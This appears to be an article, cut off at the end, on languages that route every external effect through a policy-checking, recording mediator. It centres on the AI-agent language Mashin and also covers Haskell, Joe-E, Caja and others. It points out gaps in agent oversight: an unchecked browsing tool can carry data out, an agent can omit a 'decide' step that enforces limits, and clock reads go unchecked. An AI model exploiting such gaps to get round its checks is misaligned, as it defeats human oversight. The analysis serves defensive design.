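# Can a programming language allow only checked and recorded external effects?

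## What would it mean for a language to have no ungoverned effects?

Computer programs calculate with values in their own memory, and they also act on the world outside it by fetching web pages, writing files, charging credit cards and starting other programs. In nearly every language in common use, any line of code can take such actions, and rules about them have to be added from outside the language, with a library, an operating system setting or a firewall. A few language designers have tried removing the operations for acting while leaving programs free to calculate. A program in such a language can only describe an action, and a separate part of the runtime (the software that executes the program) determines whether to carry it out. The fullest recent example is Mashin, a language for building AI agents. Alan McCann of Mashin, Inc., the company behind the language, set out its design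 in a series of papers in 2026, so most of the claims about it come from an interested party.

### From a library call to the kernel

Fetching a web page in Python takes a handful of lines. The example in Python's *http.client*, the reference page for the standard library's web client, creates a connection object for a host, calls its `request` method with a path, and reads the reply. The library opens the connection by default on the first request, so the example never does so explicitly. Most programmers use a higher-level library, either `urllib.request`, which relies on `http.client`, or the separate Requests package.

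The `http.client` module uses the `socket` module. A socket is one end of a network connection. Python's *socket* describes the module as a "straightforward transliteration" of the Unix interface, in which the methods of a socket object implement the system calls. A system call is a program's request to the kernel, the core of the operating system, which controls the network hardware. Programs usually make system calls through thin wrapper functions in the C library, as Ubuntu's *syscalls* explains. The key call for a web request is `connect`, which links the socket to a remote address, according to Linux man-pages' *connect(2)*.

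When that call arrives, the kernel can identify the process that made it (the running program as a whole) and the user account the process belongs to, but not the source file the call came from. Suppose the program also imports a small package for formatting dates. That package can import `http.client` too, or use `socket` directly, and the kernel will receive the same `connect` from the same process. The package can do this without the program's permission, and so can any package it imports. If a developer writes a wrapper that checks web requests, it checks only the requests made through it.

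### The basic terms

An *external effect* is anything a program does that changes or reads the world outside its own memory. Reading the clock is an external effect because the program's inputs do not determine the time it reads. *Pure code* computes a result from its inputs and has no external effects.

A *primitive* is an operation built into a language or its runtime that a program cannot construct from other operations. Sorting a list need not be a primitive, since any programmer can write a sorting function out of comparisons and assignments. Opening a network connection has to be one, because a program can send a packet only through a built-in operation that calls the kernel. The idea of a language with no ungoverned effects depends on this difference. Users can write a missing sorting function themselves, but if the language lacks every primitive for external effects, they cannot add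 them. Leaving out these primitives does not reduce what the language can calculate. *Intent-Driven Computing* (McCann, 2026) points out that Turing-completeness (the ability to compute anything computable) concerns the functions a language can compute and has no bearing on the effects it can cause.

The date package in the example has *ambient authority*, power that any code in a program has just by running. WASI's *Security*, a page about the standard system interface for WebAssembly programs, gives Linux and Windows as examples of systems that work this way. A process on either one inherits its user's permissions and can reach any file or network the user can, unless someone adds a sandbox.

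In the alternative design, a program produces an *effect request*, a data value that describes an action without doing it. McCann's papers call it an intent or a directive. A *mediator* inside the runtime checks the request against the *policy*, the rules for whether to allow it, deny it or hold it for approval. The mediator then records the decision in an append-only *ledger* and performs the action if the policy allows it. A *governed effect* is one that happens only after this check and leaves this record.

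A language has no ungoverned effects, then, if programs written in it can cause no other kind. McCann (2026), in *Certified Purity for Cognitive Workflow Executors*, puts the condition in temporal logic:

□ ∀d (effect_performed(d) → governance_checked(d))

Under the first formula, for every request d, whenever the action that d describes has happened, the check on d has also happened. A second formula covers the record in the same way. Both formulas apply only to requests, so they would still hold if code opened a connection without producing a request and sent data out through it. They therefore need a separate premise, which McCann states explicitly: the code that produces requests has no other means of acting.

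The components that must work correctly for any such guarantee to hold are called the *trusted computing base*. They include the mediator, since a buggy mediator could perform requests that the policy denies. They also include much of the *host*, meaning the virtual machine, operating system and native code on which the language runs.

### The reference monitor

The idea of one component that checks every access is more than fifty years old. In 1972 the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share a computer, and in many cases to write their own programs on it. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) reported the conclusions of a panel of experts who studied the problem. The central concept was the *reference monitor*, which checks every reference a program makes to other programs, data or devices against a list of what the program's user may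 do. One can picture the list as a table with a row for each user or program, a column for each file or device, and the permitted uses in the cells.

Anderson required three things of any mechanism that implements the concept. The system must always invoke it, it must be tamper-proof, and it must be small enough to analyse and test completely, because otherwise nobody can know that it checks correctly in every case.

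The first demand bears directly on language design. If some programs must run with the checks suspended, Anderson reasoned, they become part of the security apparatus and must themselves be tamper-proof and small. GCOS III, the operating system of the Honeywell 635 computer, failed this test. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but a program that needed input or output had to call the supervisor, most of which ran with the confinement switched off. The supervisor could not itself serve as the monitor, because with its supporting software it ran to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, too many for anyone to analyse fully, and several teams of testers had already broken into it.

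A language designer faces the same choice whenever someone asks for an exception, such as a fast database driver that accesses the network directly. Such an exception is an *escape hatch*, a feature that lets code bypass the rules that apply to the rest of the language, and it adds the entire driver to the trusted computing base. Anderson also spelled out limits of the reference monitor concept, which assumes that the system has identified its users correctly, that someone guards the machines and communication lines, and that the hardware works.

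### Two boundaries

In *The Two Boundaries*, McCann (2026) recasts the demand for constant checking as a comparison between two sets of effects. The *expressiveness boundary* contains every effect that a system can produce with its language, libraries and reachable services. The *governance boundary* contains every effect that the system's rules cover. Different teams usually draw the two boundaries on different schedules, and the two seldom match. Where they overlap, the system works as intended. Incidents come from effects that the system can produce but no rule covers. McCann uses the term "governance theater" for rules about things the system cannot do. Such rules may satisfy a regulator or prepare for a planned feature, but they also make the coverage look better than it is.

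His example is an AI agent with three tools, for sending email, querying a database and browsing the web. A content filter checks outgoing email for sensitive information. The browsing tool can also send information out, because a web address can carry text to whoever runs the site, but the filter does not check web requests. It does scan email subject lines for credit card numbers, although the agent has no access to any.

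Adding another rule for the browser would close that gap but not others. McCann proposes instead to make the boundaries coincide by construction, a property he calls *coterminous governance*. It requires that every effect expressible in the system pass through a governance boundary, and that the system's primitives be sufficient for the class of computations it is meant for. The second condition rules out the trivial solution of a language that is safe only because its programs can do nothing useful.

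A language can meet both conditions if programs can act only by issuing requests and every request goes to the mediator. Every action then passes through the mediator, which only has to inspect the request, a finite piece of data. It does not have to predict the behaviour of an arbitrary program, which Rice's theorem rules out in general.

This guarantees less than the phrase "the two boundaries are one" suggests. McCann holds that governance theater disappears along with the uncovered effects, but the two conditions do not imply this, since an administrator can still write a rule about a tool that nobody has connected. More seriously, the mediator checks every covered effect but may still allow it. In the example, the browser's request, including the address, would now reach the mediator, and the policy would determine the outcome. Even a policy of allowing everything would satisfy the definition.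 McCann accepts the general point and says that a governed system with a bad policy "faithfully executes the bad policy".

He also argues that nobody can add the property to an existing system as a library, because the old code would keep its direct routes to the outside. Anderson's panel had reached much the same view about operating systems, concluding that designers who do not build security in from the start have little chance of adding it later. The argument is convincing against a library, but weaker against measures that act below the language, which can close a direct route without rewriting the code that uses it.

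### Three levels at which the power can be missing

"This program cannot open a network connection" may be a guarantee about the source language, the compiled code or the running process. The three guarantees differ in what they prevent and what one has to trust.

At the **source level**, the language has no construct for an ungoverned effect, so neither the grammar nor the standard library gives a programmer a way to write one. Mashin's makers claim this in their documentation, which states that nobody can write a program that bypasses governance "because the capability to do so does not exist in the ...". McCann's small formal model in *Intent-Driven Computing* has one expression, `ask`, that submits a request. Only one evaluation rule performs an action, and it applies after a decision to allow that action.

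The absence of ungoverned effects is a property of the source programs that a compiler accepts. It does not protect against compiled code that arrives by another route, or against a program that escapes the language's restrictions while running. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2* (Anderson, 1972) discussed the second danger for computers on which users could program only in approved languages such as FORTRAN. A program able to write outside the memory set aside for its data could place instructions there and execute them, and FORTRAN's restrictions would then no longer constrain it. A secure system of this type therefore needed a strict separation of code from data, and checks on every data reference, jump and input or output transfer.

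At the **compiled-code level**, it would mean that the compiled program cannot itself cause external effects, whatever compiler or person produced it. Mashin compiles to bytecode for the BEAM, the Erlang virtual machine, and that bytecode can cause effects. McCann identifies five classes of mechanism by which a BEAM module can do so even when its imports look harmless. His remedy is to compile the modules that execute a program's steps to WebAssembly, a portable bytecode format, and to admit only those whose imports all appear on a list of pure functions. WebAssembly suits this purpose because, according to the WebAssembly project, it specifies no system calls, only a way to import functions that the host environment defines. A WebAssembly component without a network import cannot open a socket, and anyone can inspect the file to confirm that the import is missing. Python's reference pages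 for `socket` and `http.client` are both marked "not WASI" (WebAssembly System Interface) because a programmer can still write the call, but the platform provides nothing to carry it out.

At the **process level**, the operating system refuses the action no matter which code in the process attempts it. On Linux, seccomp filters the system calls a process makes, and the man page *socketcall(2)* mentions filters for socket calls in particular. This level matters because a WebAssembly module runs inside a host process that can usually open connections. The host chooses which functions to supply, and a flaw in a supposedly pure one could give the module more access than its import list suggests.

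The levels do not imply one another, as a few combinations make clear.

| | Source language has no construct | Compiled code has no power | Running process has no power |
|---|---|---|---|
| Python on Linux | No | No | No |
| Mashin compiled to BEAM bytecode | Yes, by design | No | No |
| WebAssembly module with only pure imports | Depends on the language | Yes | No |
| Python under a filter that blocks socket calls | No | No | Yes, for sockets |

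The process-wide filter in the last row also blocks the mediator if the mediator runs in that process. A governed language can therefore reach the process level only by running pure code and the mediator in separate processes. McCann describes such a split and leaves it as future work.

Each level also requires trust in different software: the compiler and runtime, the WebAssembly engine and its imported functions, or the kernel. For the WebAssembly version of Mashin, McCann names five trusted components: the engine, the functions it supplies to modules, the list of permitted functions, the gate that inspects modules before they run, and the mediator. McCann does not include the BEAM or the operating system, although the gate and the mediator depend on both.

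### Why AI agents made the question pressing

Programmers have lived with ambient authority for decades. McCann thinks that it was harmless as long as a human wrote every line, and that it became a problem once autonomous systems began to generate their behaviour as they ran, with no fixed point between deciding to act and acting. This understates the earlier risk, since humans wrote the date-formatting package and the Air Force panel was worried about human programmers. But an agent that writes and runs code does resemble the user the panel feared, who had legitimate access to the machine and could run arbitrary programs on it. The agent need not be malicious. It may have misunderstood its task, or it may be following instructions that an attacker planted in a document it was reading.

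Agents also make rules harder to write. A web server's abilities stay the same until someone updates its code, so its owners can write a policy for a known list of abilities. An agent combines its tools in sequences nobody foresaw, and each new tool multiplies the combinations.

Ungoverned effects also weaken accountability. McCann imagines an agent that handles 200 refund requests a day at a financial firm, with access to email, customer records and a payment system. For every refund, the compliance team wants proof that the agent had authority to issue it, consulted the policy and stayed out of records it had no right to see. If the agent runs in ordinary Python, the firm's access keys limit what it can reach but do not record why anyone granted the access. The logs list what the agent did, but the team cannot use them to prove that the list is complete, because the code can act directly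 without writing a log entry.

McCann also calculates that if monitoring covers 99 percent of the ways an agent can act, the chance of at least one uncovered action among n is 1 − 0.99ⁿ, or 63 percent after 100 actions and 99.996 percent after 1,000. The formula treats every action as an independent draw. An agent that repeats a few familiar steps would have a much lower chance of taking an uncovered action, and one that keeps looking for another way to finish a blocked task could have a higher chance.

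## Which earlier languages gave programs no direct way to act?

Language designers were removing programs' ability to act directly long before AI agents became common. Some wanted functions to behave like mathematical functions, and others wanted to run untrusted code safely. Several of their languages show that people can write useful programs without direct access to files or networks. But none of them, from early Haskell to Dhall, required every action to be checked against a policy and recorded, although in some a programmer could have added both with little work.

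### Haskell's lists of requests and responses

Haskell is a purely functional language. It is also lazy, so it evaluates an expression only when something needs the value. Laziness makes ordinary side effects unworkable. *Tackling the Awkward Squad* (Peyton Jones, 2001) gives the example of a list with two elements, each of which would print a character when evaluated. If the program computes only the length of the list, nothing prints, because finding the length does not require evaluating the elements.

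Haskell's designers therefore moved effects out of the program. In the first versions of the language, a whole program was a function of this type:

```haskell
main :: [Response] -> [Request]
```

The square brackets denote lists. A `Request` is a data value such as `ReadFile "motd"`, and a `Response` holds the outcome, such as the text of the file or an error. These are effect requests in the full sense. Hackage's *System.IO.Dialogue* (2022), a library that rebuilds the model in modern Haskell, quotes the language report of the time, in which a program "issues a stream of requests to the operating system". A program that reads a file and displays it needs only a few lines:

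```haskell
main responses = [ReadFile "motd", display (head responses)]

display (Str text)    = AppendChan stdout text
display (Failure err) = AppendChan stdout "cannot read the file"
```

Lazy evaluation lets the program take as its input the responses to requests it has not yet made, even though the definition looks circular. A wrapper program outside Haskell takes the first request, which depends on no response, reads the file and puts the contents at the head of the response list. The wrapper evaluates the second request only after that, so `display` is applied to a response that has already arrived.

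The wrapper performs every action, and it receives the complete request before doing so. *Interpreting synchronized streams (pre-IO monad Haskell)*, a message to a Haskell mailing list, contains a small wrapper built around a function with one case for each kind of request. A policy check and a line of logging could be added before those cases, and a program that could act only through its request list could not bypass them. Haskell's designers removed direct effects and supplied a wrapper, but they did not intend it to check or record requests, and they gave it neither a policy nor a log.

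The model lasted until 1996, and Peyton Jones describes three defects. One is that requests and responses could easily fall out of step. If a programmer adds a request to print "Reading the file" at the start of the list above, the first response reports that the printing succeeded. `display` has no case for that response, so the program fails at run time. The compiler cannot catch the mistake because every response has the same type. Another defect is that a program could block itself. If `main` inspects the response list before producing any request, it waits for a response to a request it has not issued.

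Ordinary users of early Haskell could not add new kinds of effect. The `Request` type listed every possible action, so supporting network sockets meant adding entries to `Request` and `Response` and changing the wrapper that carried out requests. Programmers could also attach two functions to each request, one for success and one for failure, which kept each response next to its request. But that style translated into the same lists of requests and responses and allowed only the same fixed set of actions.

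Monadic input and output replaced both styles. A value of type `IO a` is an action that, when performed, may do input or output and then delivers a value of type `a`. An operator joins two actions by performing the first and passing its result to a function that returns the next. Each action can have its own result type, and each result goes directly to the code that needs it, so results cannot be matched with the wrong actions.

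Peyton Jones answers the third problem differently. He concedes that the number of possible input and output primitives is unbounded, and concludes that Haskell needs a way to call arbitrary libraries supplied by the operating system. This suits programmers, but it gives up two properties that would be useful in a governed language. The first is a closed list of requests, which lets an administrator review every kind of action and prevents anyone from adding one without changing the mediator. The second is that a `Request` is plain data that a wrapper can examine, whereas an `IO` action is opaque and can only be performed or joined to others.

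Haskell later added `unsafePerformIO`, which lets supposedly pure code perform an action. *Noether*, a set of slides on the design of a new language, includes a few lines of code that use this function to crash the Glasgow Haskell runtime. A later mode of Haskell, Safe Haskell, was designed to exclude such functions.

### Object capabilities in E and Joe-E

Other designers left the actions in the language and restricted which code could reach them. In an object-capability language, every file and network connection is an object, and code can use an object only if it holds a reference to it. Code gets a reference by creating a new object or by receiving the reference from code that already has it, and cannot make one up from a name or a memory address. *Two E language implementations* traces E, the language that most influenced later object-capability languages, to Mark Miller, Dan Bornstein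 and others at Electric Communities in 1997.

*Joe-E* (Mettler, Wagner and Close, 2010) applied E's discipline to Java by removing features. Every Joe-E program is a Java program that passes an extra checker, the verifier, which examines each source file separately and doesn't change it. The standard Java compiler and virtual machine compile and run the program.

Most of the danger came from Java's standard library. Java's `File` constructor turns any string into an object that can read, overwrite or delete the file with that name. Joe-E forbids the constructor, so code has to receive a `File` object, typically as an argument from another part of the program. Joe-E also forbids Java's `getParentFile` method. A `File` for a directory should give access only to that directory and its contents, but `getParentFile` returns the directory above, and repeated calls reach the root of the disk.

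Another constructor takes a directory and the name of a file inside it. If the directory is null, Java treats the name as an absolute path, so a program can open any file on the disk. A wrapper that rejects null replaces this constructor. This work is called *taming*, and it produces a list of approved classes, constructors, methods and fields. The verifier rejects any program that refers to a library feature outside the list.

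Joe-E also restricts the language itself. Static fields, Java's global variables, may hold only immutable data, because any code could use a capability stored in one. Joe-E code cannot define native methods, which run outside Java's memory protection, and it cannot use reflection to read another object's private fields. Exceptions must be immutable too. Otherwise a method that received a private capability could attach it to an exception, which could carry it past the method's caller to code that should never have it.

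These rules give a strong guarantee about code that receives no capabilities. Mettler and colleagues describe an image viewer with downloadable decoders. Each decoder must implement an interface that takes an array of bytes and returns a bitmap. A malicious decoder can return the wrong picture, but it cannot send a packet, write a file or carry data from one image to the next. It can still use up memory and processor time, which Joe-E does not limit.

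Joe-E removes ambient authority, so code has no direct effects by default, but code that holds a capability acts directly. For example, a method with a `File` object writes to the disk by calling the object, without sending a request to a mediator.

Joe-E also does not require programs to check or record their external effects, though a programmer can add both. Mettler and colleagues present a short append-only log class and explain that a reviewer would need to read only the component that dispatches requests to confirm that a server logs every incoming network request. In ordinary Java, the same class would guarantee much less, since code elsewhere could use reflection to reach the log's private buffer and erase entries.

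### What reviews and case studies found

Taming requires people to judge every library method, and they make mistakes. Miller (2006) notes in *Robust Composition*, his thesis on E, that the US defence research agency DARPA sponsored a security review of E and two associated programs, CapDesk and the DarpaBrowser. According to Mettler and colleagues, the reviewers found that E's list of approved Java methods included several that broke capability discipline. *Noether* adds that the review found information leaking through conventional exception handling, outside the control of any capability.

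Mettler and colleagues approved methods more cautiously, but they acknowledge that they may have approved some unsafe ones. They call taming, the process of deciding which methods are safe to expose, "a substantial weakness in our approach". Any language that relies on a list of safe functions has the same problem, including the version of Mashin that decides which WebAssembly modules to accept by checking their imports.

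Joe-E's guarantee is also limited to source code. Joe-E checks source because Java bytecode can do things that no Java program can, which makes bytecode harder to reason about. If a program mixes Joe-E with unrestricted Java, the Java code can break the Joe-E code's protections, and a reviewer has to examine the Java code as carefully as they would without Joe-E.

Case studies of Joe-E suggest that programmers can work within its restrictions. In earlier work, Joe-E's designers had ported an open-source HTML parser of more than 10,000 lines, and the ported version was deterministic and had no side effects. A more demanding test was Waterken, a server on which mutually distrustful web applications can share one Java virtual machine. It has about 13,000 lines of Joe-E and 4,000 lines of ordinary Java, so nearly a quarter of the code was not subject to the verifier's rules.

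Removing hidden effects also has benefits in Waterken that have little to do with stopping attackers. The server treats each event an application handles as a transaction, and either saves all the resulting changes or discards them all. It can find every change because applications cannot keep state in global variables or write to a file unobserved. To support web caching, the server labels each response with a hash of the application's code and all the stored data the response depends on. The same label always means the same response because the code cannot read a clock or use any other source of nondeterminism.

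Joe-E's designers did not find its restrictions a serious problem, but they were writing their own software with a method they knew well. They expect most programmers to need training in capability design. They aimed Joe-E at new code because most existing Java would not pass the verifier.

### The case against a central policy

Some supporters of capabilities reject a compulsory central policy on principle. In *Lambda Capabilities*, Leonard explains capabilities using ordinary functions. The programmer passes a component a small function that uses a resource on its behalf, instead of giving the component direct access. That function can reject certain values, stop working after three uses, or log each call with a label for the component that made it. Leonard sees no need for a separate policy language on top of these functions, and gives reasons to avoid one.

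A web server must read its private encryption key but must never send the key to a visitor. A visitor might request a web address containing a path to the key file. A policy for the whole server has to allow the read, so it cannot prevent the leak. With capabilities, only the encryption library holds the directory that contains the key, and the code that answers visitors holds only the directory of web pages. Leonard also warns that forbidding a component to use a reference it already holds encourages passing the reference to more privileged code. He considers this the root of many real attacks, in which a harmful link works only when a victim with the right permissions follows it.

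The web server example counts against any mediator that judges a request only by the action it describes. A mediator could avoid this problem if each request also identified the component that issued it and the authority that component had received, but the mediator would then do much of what a capability system does.

Leonard's wrappers would not satisfy a compliance team that needs a complete record unless someone confirmed that the program had wrapped every payment capability before handing it out. Leonard is applying these principles to Eio, an input and output library for OCaml, but does not expect OCaml to become capability-secure any time soon. Until it does, a malicious package can ignore these principles.

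### What became of Caja

Google's Caja brought object capabilities to JavaScript. Websites generally stripped scripts out of third-party content, and *Caja* (Miller, Samuel and colleagues, 2008) proposed a way for web applications to accept them. Caja defined a safe subset of JavaScript and translated older code into it. Google said it let websites control what embedded code could do with user data. Embedded code lost its ambient authority, and the embedding site decided which capabilities to supply and whether to check or log their use.

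In November 2017 the sandbox failed completely. Reid (2017), in *Caja Security Advisory 2017-11-14*, explained that browsers had added an `import` expression and new kinds of function, both of which offered ways to execute code from a string. SES (Secure ECMAScript), the restricted form of JavaScript that Caja used, did not account for these features and could not block them. The developers responded by parsing and rewriting all incoming code to allow only constructs they understood. As a result, error messages no longer gave useful positions in the source.

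Caja's developers had been removing known dangers from a language that other people were still extending, and any extension could restore a power they had removed. A checker that accepts only known constructs avoids this problem because it rejects new features until someone has examined them. Its maintainers must also keep up with changes to the host language for as long as anyone uses the checker.

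Google announced that it would archive Caja on 31 January 2021 and stop issuing security patches. It explained that nobody had kept the project up to date with web security research, and that Google engineers and outsiders had reported several vulnerabilities. Software that still depended on Caja was exposed. Launchpad's *CVE 2021-32798* describes how a malicious file could run code on the computer of anyone who opened it in Jupyter Notebook, a popular data analysis tool that used an outdated version of Caja to clean its input.

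*Google Caja*, a retrospective by one of the developers, credits `Object.freeze`, a standard JavaScript function that makes an object unchangeable, to Mark Miller's advocacy. Work on Caja's ideas has continued since the product ended, under the names Secure ECMAScript and Hardened JavaScript, with funding from Agoric, a company that uses it to run blockchain contracts.

### Monte and Misty

Monte, a descendant of E, makes a program's powers visible at its entry point. Monte's *Practical Security II* describes a chat bot that runs the party game Mafia. The bot's `main` function receives the powers to open network connections, look up addresses, set timers and obtain secure random numbers as named arguments. It then gives each component narrower powers. For example, the code that moderates a game receives a random-number generator and two chat channels, but not the power to open network connections.

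A reader can therefore learn most of what the bot might do from one argument list. The list leaves out printing, which is also an external effect, because several components call `traceln`, which prints debugging output, without receiving it as an argument. Monte does not require a check or a record of any of these effects, and code that holds a network capability uses it directly.

Misty, designed by Douglas Crockford, combines capabilities with a policy, at least in outline. *Misty Programming Language* attributes the security of a Misty system to "capability discipline and a policy machine". Its capability rules closely follow E's. Code can obtain a reference only by receiving it from its creator, constructing the object itself, or receiving it from another object that it already deals with. A programmer can place a *facet*, an intermediary that filters or checks requests, in front of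 a powerful object. A facet for the file system might allow access only to certain directories or limit file sizes.

*Misty Programming Language* is much vaguer about the policy machine. It mentions policies only for guest programs, which come from another party. The system compiles a guest's source code under the most restrictive policies. The running guest cannot create more actors (Misty's isolated processes) and can send messages only to its home system. *Misty Programming Language* doesn't describe a ledger or a component that examines every request. Like Joe-E, Misty thus gives programs no ambient authority, with checks wherever a programmer installs a facet.

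### Starlark and Dhall

Configuration languages can remove more effects, because a configuration file only has to produce data. Starlark, a small dialect of Python that Google developed for its build tool Bazel, has no built-in way to open a file, use the network or read the clock. However, an application that embeds Starlark can add its own functions, so the guarantee holds only if those functions are harmless.

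Bazel's ordinary build rules show effect requests working at industrial scale. A rule written in Starlark registers an action instead of running a compiler itself. The action describes a command and its input and output files, and Bazel runs the command later if the build needs the output. Bazel makes that decision to avoid unnecessary work, not to enforce a policy on which commands are acceptable, and the command is an ordinary program with whatever access the operating system or a sandbox allows. Rules that fetch outside dependencies can do more, because Bazel gives them functions that download files and execute programs immediately. Starlark itself gives programs no direct way to cause effects, but the application that runs it has to do any checking or recording.

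Dhall is a configuration language whose programs always terminate. It has no functions for input or output, but evaluating a Dhall file can still cause network traffic because the file can import an expression from a web address. The interpreter fetches that expression before it evaluates the rest of the file. Imports can also read local files and environment variables.

Dhall's designers restricted imports to limit the danger. An import's address is fixed text in the source, so a program cannot compute one that contains a secret. A file fetched from the web cannot import the user's environment variables. If a programmer attaches a cryptographic hash to an import, the interpreter rejects any content that does not match it.

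These checks are not a policy that an administrator sets, and Dhall keeps no ledger of what the interpreter fetched. Imports can also send data out. A request may include a header containing an environment variable, such as the access token for a private repository, and even a bare request reveals to the server that someone is loading the file. Because this happens before the program runs, a mediator that handled only the requests of running programs would miss it. A governed language with remote imports would have to send those through the mediator too.

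## How does a program act if it can only make requests?

An early Haskell program sent out one list of requests and read the outcomes from another, and the programmer had to match each outcome to its request. McCann also treats requests as data in *Intent-Driven Computing*, but in his model each request gets its own reply after the mediator decides what to do with that request. The program waits at each request for the reply, which can take days if a person has to approve the action.

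### A request is a value

McCann defines an effect request as a finite data value with four parts:

i = (action, target, params, context)

For a refund of $120, the action could be an HTTP POST (the web's usual way of submitting data), and the target could be the address of a payment company's refund service. The parameters could be the order number and the amount, and the context could identify the agent and the customer it is dealing with.

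A request is a value that code can store, print or compare with another without moving any money. Code that calls an ordinary Python function to pay refunds cannot inspect beforehand what the function will send. McCann requires the context to be finite and storable too, so that every check terminates and someone can repeat it later from the record.

### A calculus with one effectful term

McCann describes the model with a calculus, a language cut down to the few constructs needed to reason about it. A program is an expression *e* of one of these forms:

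```
e ::= x | v | let x = e₁ in e₂ | if e₁ then e₂ else e₃
    | compute(e) | ask(a, t, p)
```

Here *x* is a variable and *v* is a finished value, such as a number, a piece of text, a function or a request. Only `ask` reaches outside the program. It takes an action, a target and parameters, so the runtime has to supply the fourth part of the request, the context. A program can also build a request and keep it in a variable, but no rule acts on a request just because it exists.

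The state of a running program is a triple ⟨e, P, L⟩ of the expression still to evaluate, the policy and the ledger. The mediator is a function G. Given the policy, a request i and the runtime's context c, it returns a decision and a record r. Four rules say how the triple changes:

```
Pure:      ⟨e, P, L⟩             →  ⟨e′, P, L⟩
           if e becomes e′ by one step of calculation

Allow:     ⟨ask(a, t, p), P, L⟩  →  ⟨v, P, L·r⟩
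           if G(P, i, c) = (allow, r) and realize(i) = v

Deny:      ⟨ask(a, t, p), P, L⟩  →  ⟨denied, P, L·r⟩
           if G(P, i, c) = (deny, r)

Escalate:  ⟨ask(a, t, p), P, L⟩  →  ⟨suspended, P, L·r⟩
           if G(P, i, c) = (escalate, r)
```

L·r is the ledger with the new record added at the end. The operation `realize`, which performs an action, appears only in the Allow rule, and McCann's theorems about bypassing the mediator depend on that.

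The calculus has functions but no syntax for applying them, no expression that tests whether a reply is `denied`, and no rule for leaving `suspended`. These gaps leave open what a program does after a refusal or an approval, but they don't let any effect bypass the mediator.

### One refund at three amounts

Suppose that a company's policy allows refunds of up to $200, holds those between $200 and $500 for a person to approve, and refuses anything larger. The $500 limit comes from a refund agent that McCann tested on simulated cases, and the $200 threshold is only for illustration. With a little extra notation for records and text, the program is:

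```
let amount = compute(price - fee) in
let reply  = ask(post, "https://payments.example.com/refunds",
                 {order: "A-1041", amount: amount}) in
compute("Refund number " + reply.id)
```

If the price is $130 and the fee $10, the Pure rule reduces the first line to 120 and leaves the policy and ledger unchanged. The program then reaches `ask`. The mediator allows the request, the runtime sends it, and the payment company returns a record with the refund number R-77. Under the Allow rule, this record replaces the whole `ask` expression, and the ledger gains one entry. The last line is also pure and produces "Refund number R-77".

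The Escalate rule applies at $350. The ledger gains an entry, but the runtime sends nothing, and `suspended` takes the place of the reply. The last line cannot run without a refund number, so the program waits.

For a $900 refund, the Deny rule returns `denied` instead of the reply. The program then tries to read a refund number from `denied` and fails. Its author should have planned for refusals, which are routine in a system like this. In McCann's simulation, 200 customer cases led to 847 effect requests, of which the mediator allowed 423, refused 312 and held 112, so just over half did not go through at once. Some of the refused requests were for refunds above the limit, and others were for customer records that the agent had no right to see.

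A held request can also go out of date. A manager might approve the $350 refund on Thursday without knowing that a colleague paid it by hand on Wednesday. *Authority at Commit Time* (2026) proposes that an action take effect only if everything it declares as a dependency is still current when the runtime decides whether to admit it. Other changes do not block the action, so the rule protects only against changes in things that someone thought to declare. *Runtime Control for AI Agents* (2026) has a similar rule in a claims-handling system, where revising the amount to $7,200 cancels the earlier permission to pay and forces a new decision. McCann's calculus lacks a rule for resuming a suspended program, and that rule would need a similar check.

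### The same program in Mashin

A Mashin program is called a machine, and its file declares what the machine accepts, what it returns, what it may do and which steps it takes. The refund program could look like this:

```
machine send_refund
  accepts
    order_id as text, is required
    amount as number, is required

  responds with
    result as text

  ensures
    permissions
      allowed to http

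  implements
    ask pay, from: "@mashin/actions/http/post"
      url: "https://payments.example.com/refunds"
      body: {order: input.order_id, amount: input.amount}
      returns
        body as map
      assuming
        body: {id: "R-77"}

    compute done
      {result: "Refund number " + steps.pay.body.id}

    on failure
      compute not_done
        {result: error.type + " at " + error.step}
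```

The `ask` step makes the request, and the `compute` steps only calculate. According to Mashin's *ask ... from*, the `returns` lines declare the fields the reply should have, and the `assuming` lines supply a made-up reply for tests. Mashin's *action* documents a second way to write the same kind of request, with an example program that charges a credit card. Another form of `ask` sends a task to a language model, and the mediator checks that request too.

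If the mediator allows the refund, later steps can read the reply as `steps.pay`. If it refuses, execution jumps to the `on failure` block, where `error.type` is "permission_denied" and `error.step` is the name of the failed step, as Mashin's *on failure* explains. Without such a block, the machine halts. If the policy requires approval, Mashin's *Governance* states that the machine pauses, shows the request to the user and continues only after approval. Programmers can also suspend a machine themselves. According to Mashin's *wait for*, the runtime then saves the machine's state and position in a database and shuts the process down. When the awaited event arrives, a new process continues from the next step, so a program that waits three days for a manager uses no memory while waiting.

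However, nothing in this program distinguishes $120 from $900. The permissions listed in Mashin's *ensures* name kinds of action, such as `http` or `db_write`, not amounts. Moving `http` to the list that requires approval would hold every refund, however small. The Mashin documentation does set limits on amounts, at 500 and 10,000, but in a `decide` step, which is part of the program's own code. Whoever writes the program can leave that step out, and the writer may be the AI agent the limits were meant to restrain. McCann measured the speed of policies that include numeric comparisons, so the mediator can evaluate such rules, but the permission syntax has no way to state one.

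The pure side has a smaller gap. Mashin's *compute* states that the same inputs always produce the same output, so `compute` steps never need permission. But Mashin's *Expression Language* lists two exceptions, `DateTime.now()` and `Math.random()`. Reading the clock is an external effect, and here it happens without a policy check. It cannot send anything out, but it can change what a program requests, for example when refunds are available for only 30 days. The runtime could close this gap by supplying the time as an input.

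McCann's accounts of refusal also differ. In the proofs in *Mechanized Foundations of Structural Governance* (McCann, 2026), a refused request never returns, because the model enters a silent infinite loop. In his specification of the working interpreter, a refusal halts the sequence of requests. In the calculus, a refused request returns `denied`, and in the documentation, the program can recover. The forbidden action does not happen in any of the four versions. But a program that learns of a refusal can try something else, so the proofs model refusals more simply than Mashin handles them.

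### Algebraic effects and free monads

Programs that describe operations for other code to perform are an old idea in functional programming. With *algebraic effects*, a program performs a named operation, and a surrounding piece of code, the *handler*, determines what the operation means. Skuld, a library for Elixir, gives a small example:

```elixir
comp do
  name <- Reader.ask()
  "Hello, #{name}!"
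end
|> Reader.with_handler("World")
```

The first part requests a name without fixing where it comes from. The last line attaches a handler that supplies "World", and running the result gives "Hello, World!". In the general form of the technique, a handler also receives the rest of the computation, which it can resume with a reply, abandon or keep for later. McCann's mediator fits this description because it resumes the program with a result or a refusal, or keeps it until someone approves.

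A *free monad* turns the program itself into a data structure. Such a program is either a finished value or a request joined to a function that takes the reply and returns the rest of the program. McCann's proofs use a close relative, the interaction tree:

```
itree E R ::= Ret(v) | Tau(t) | Vis(e, k)
```

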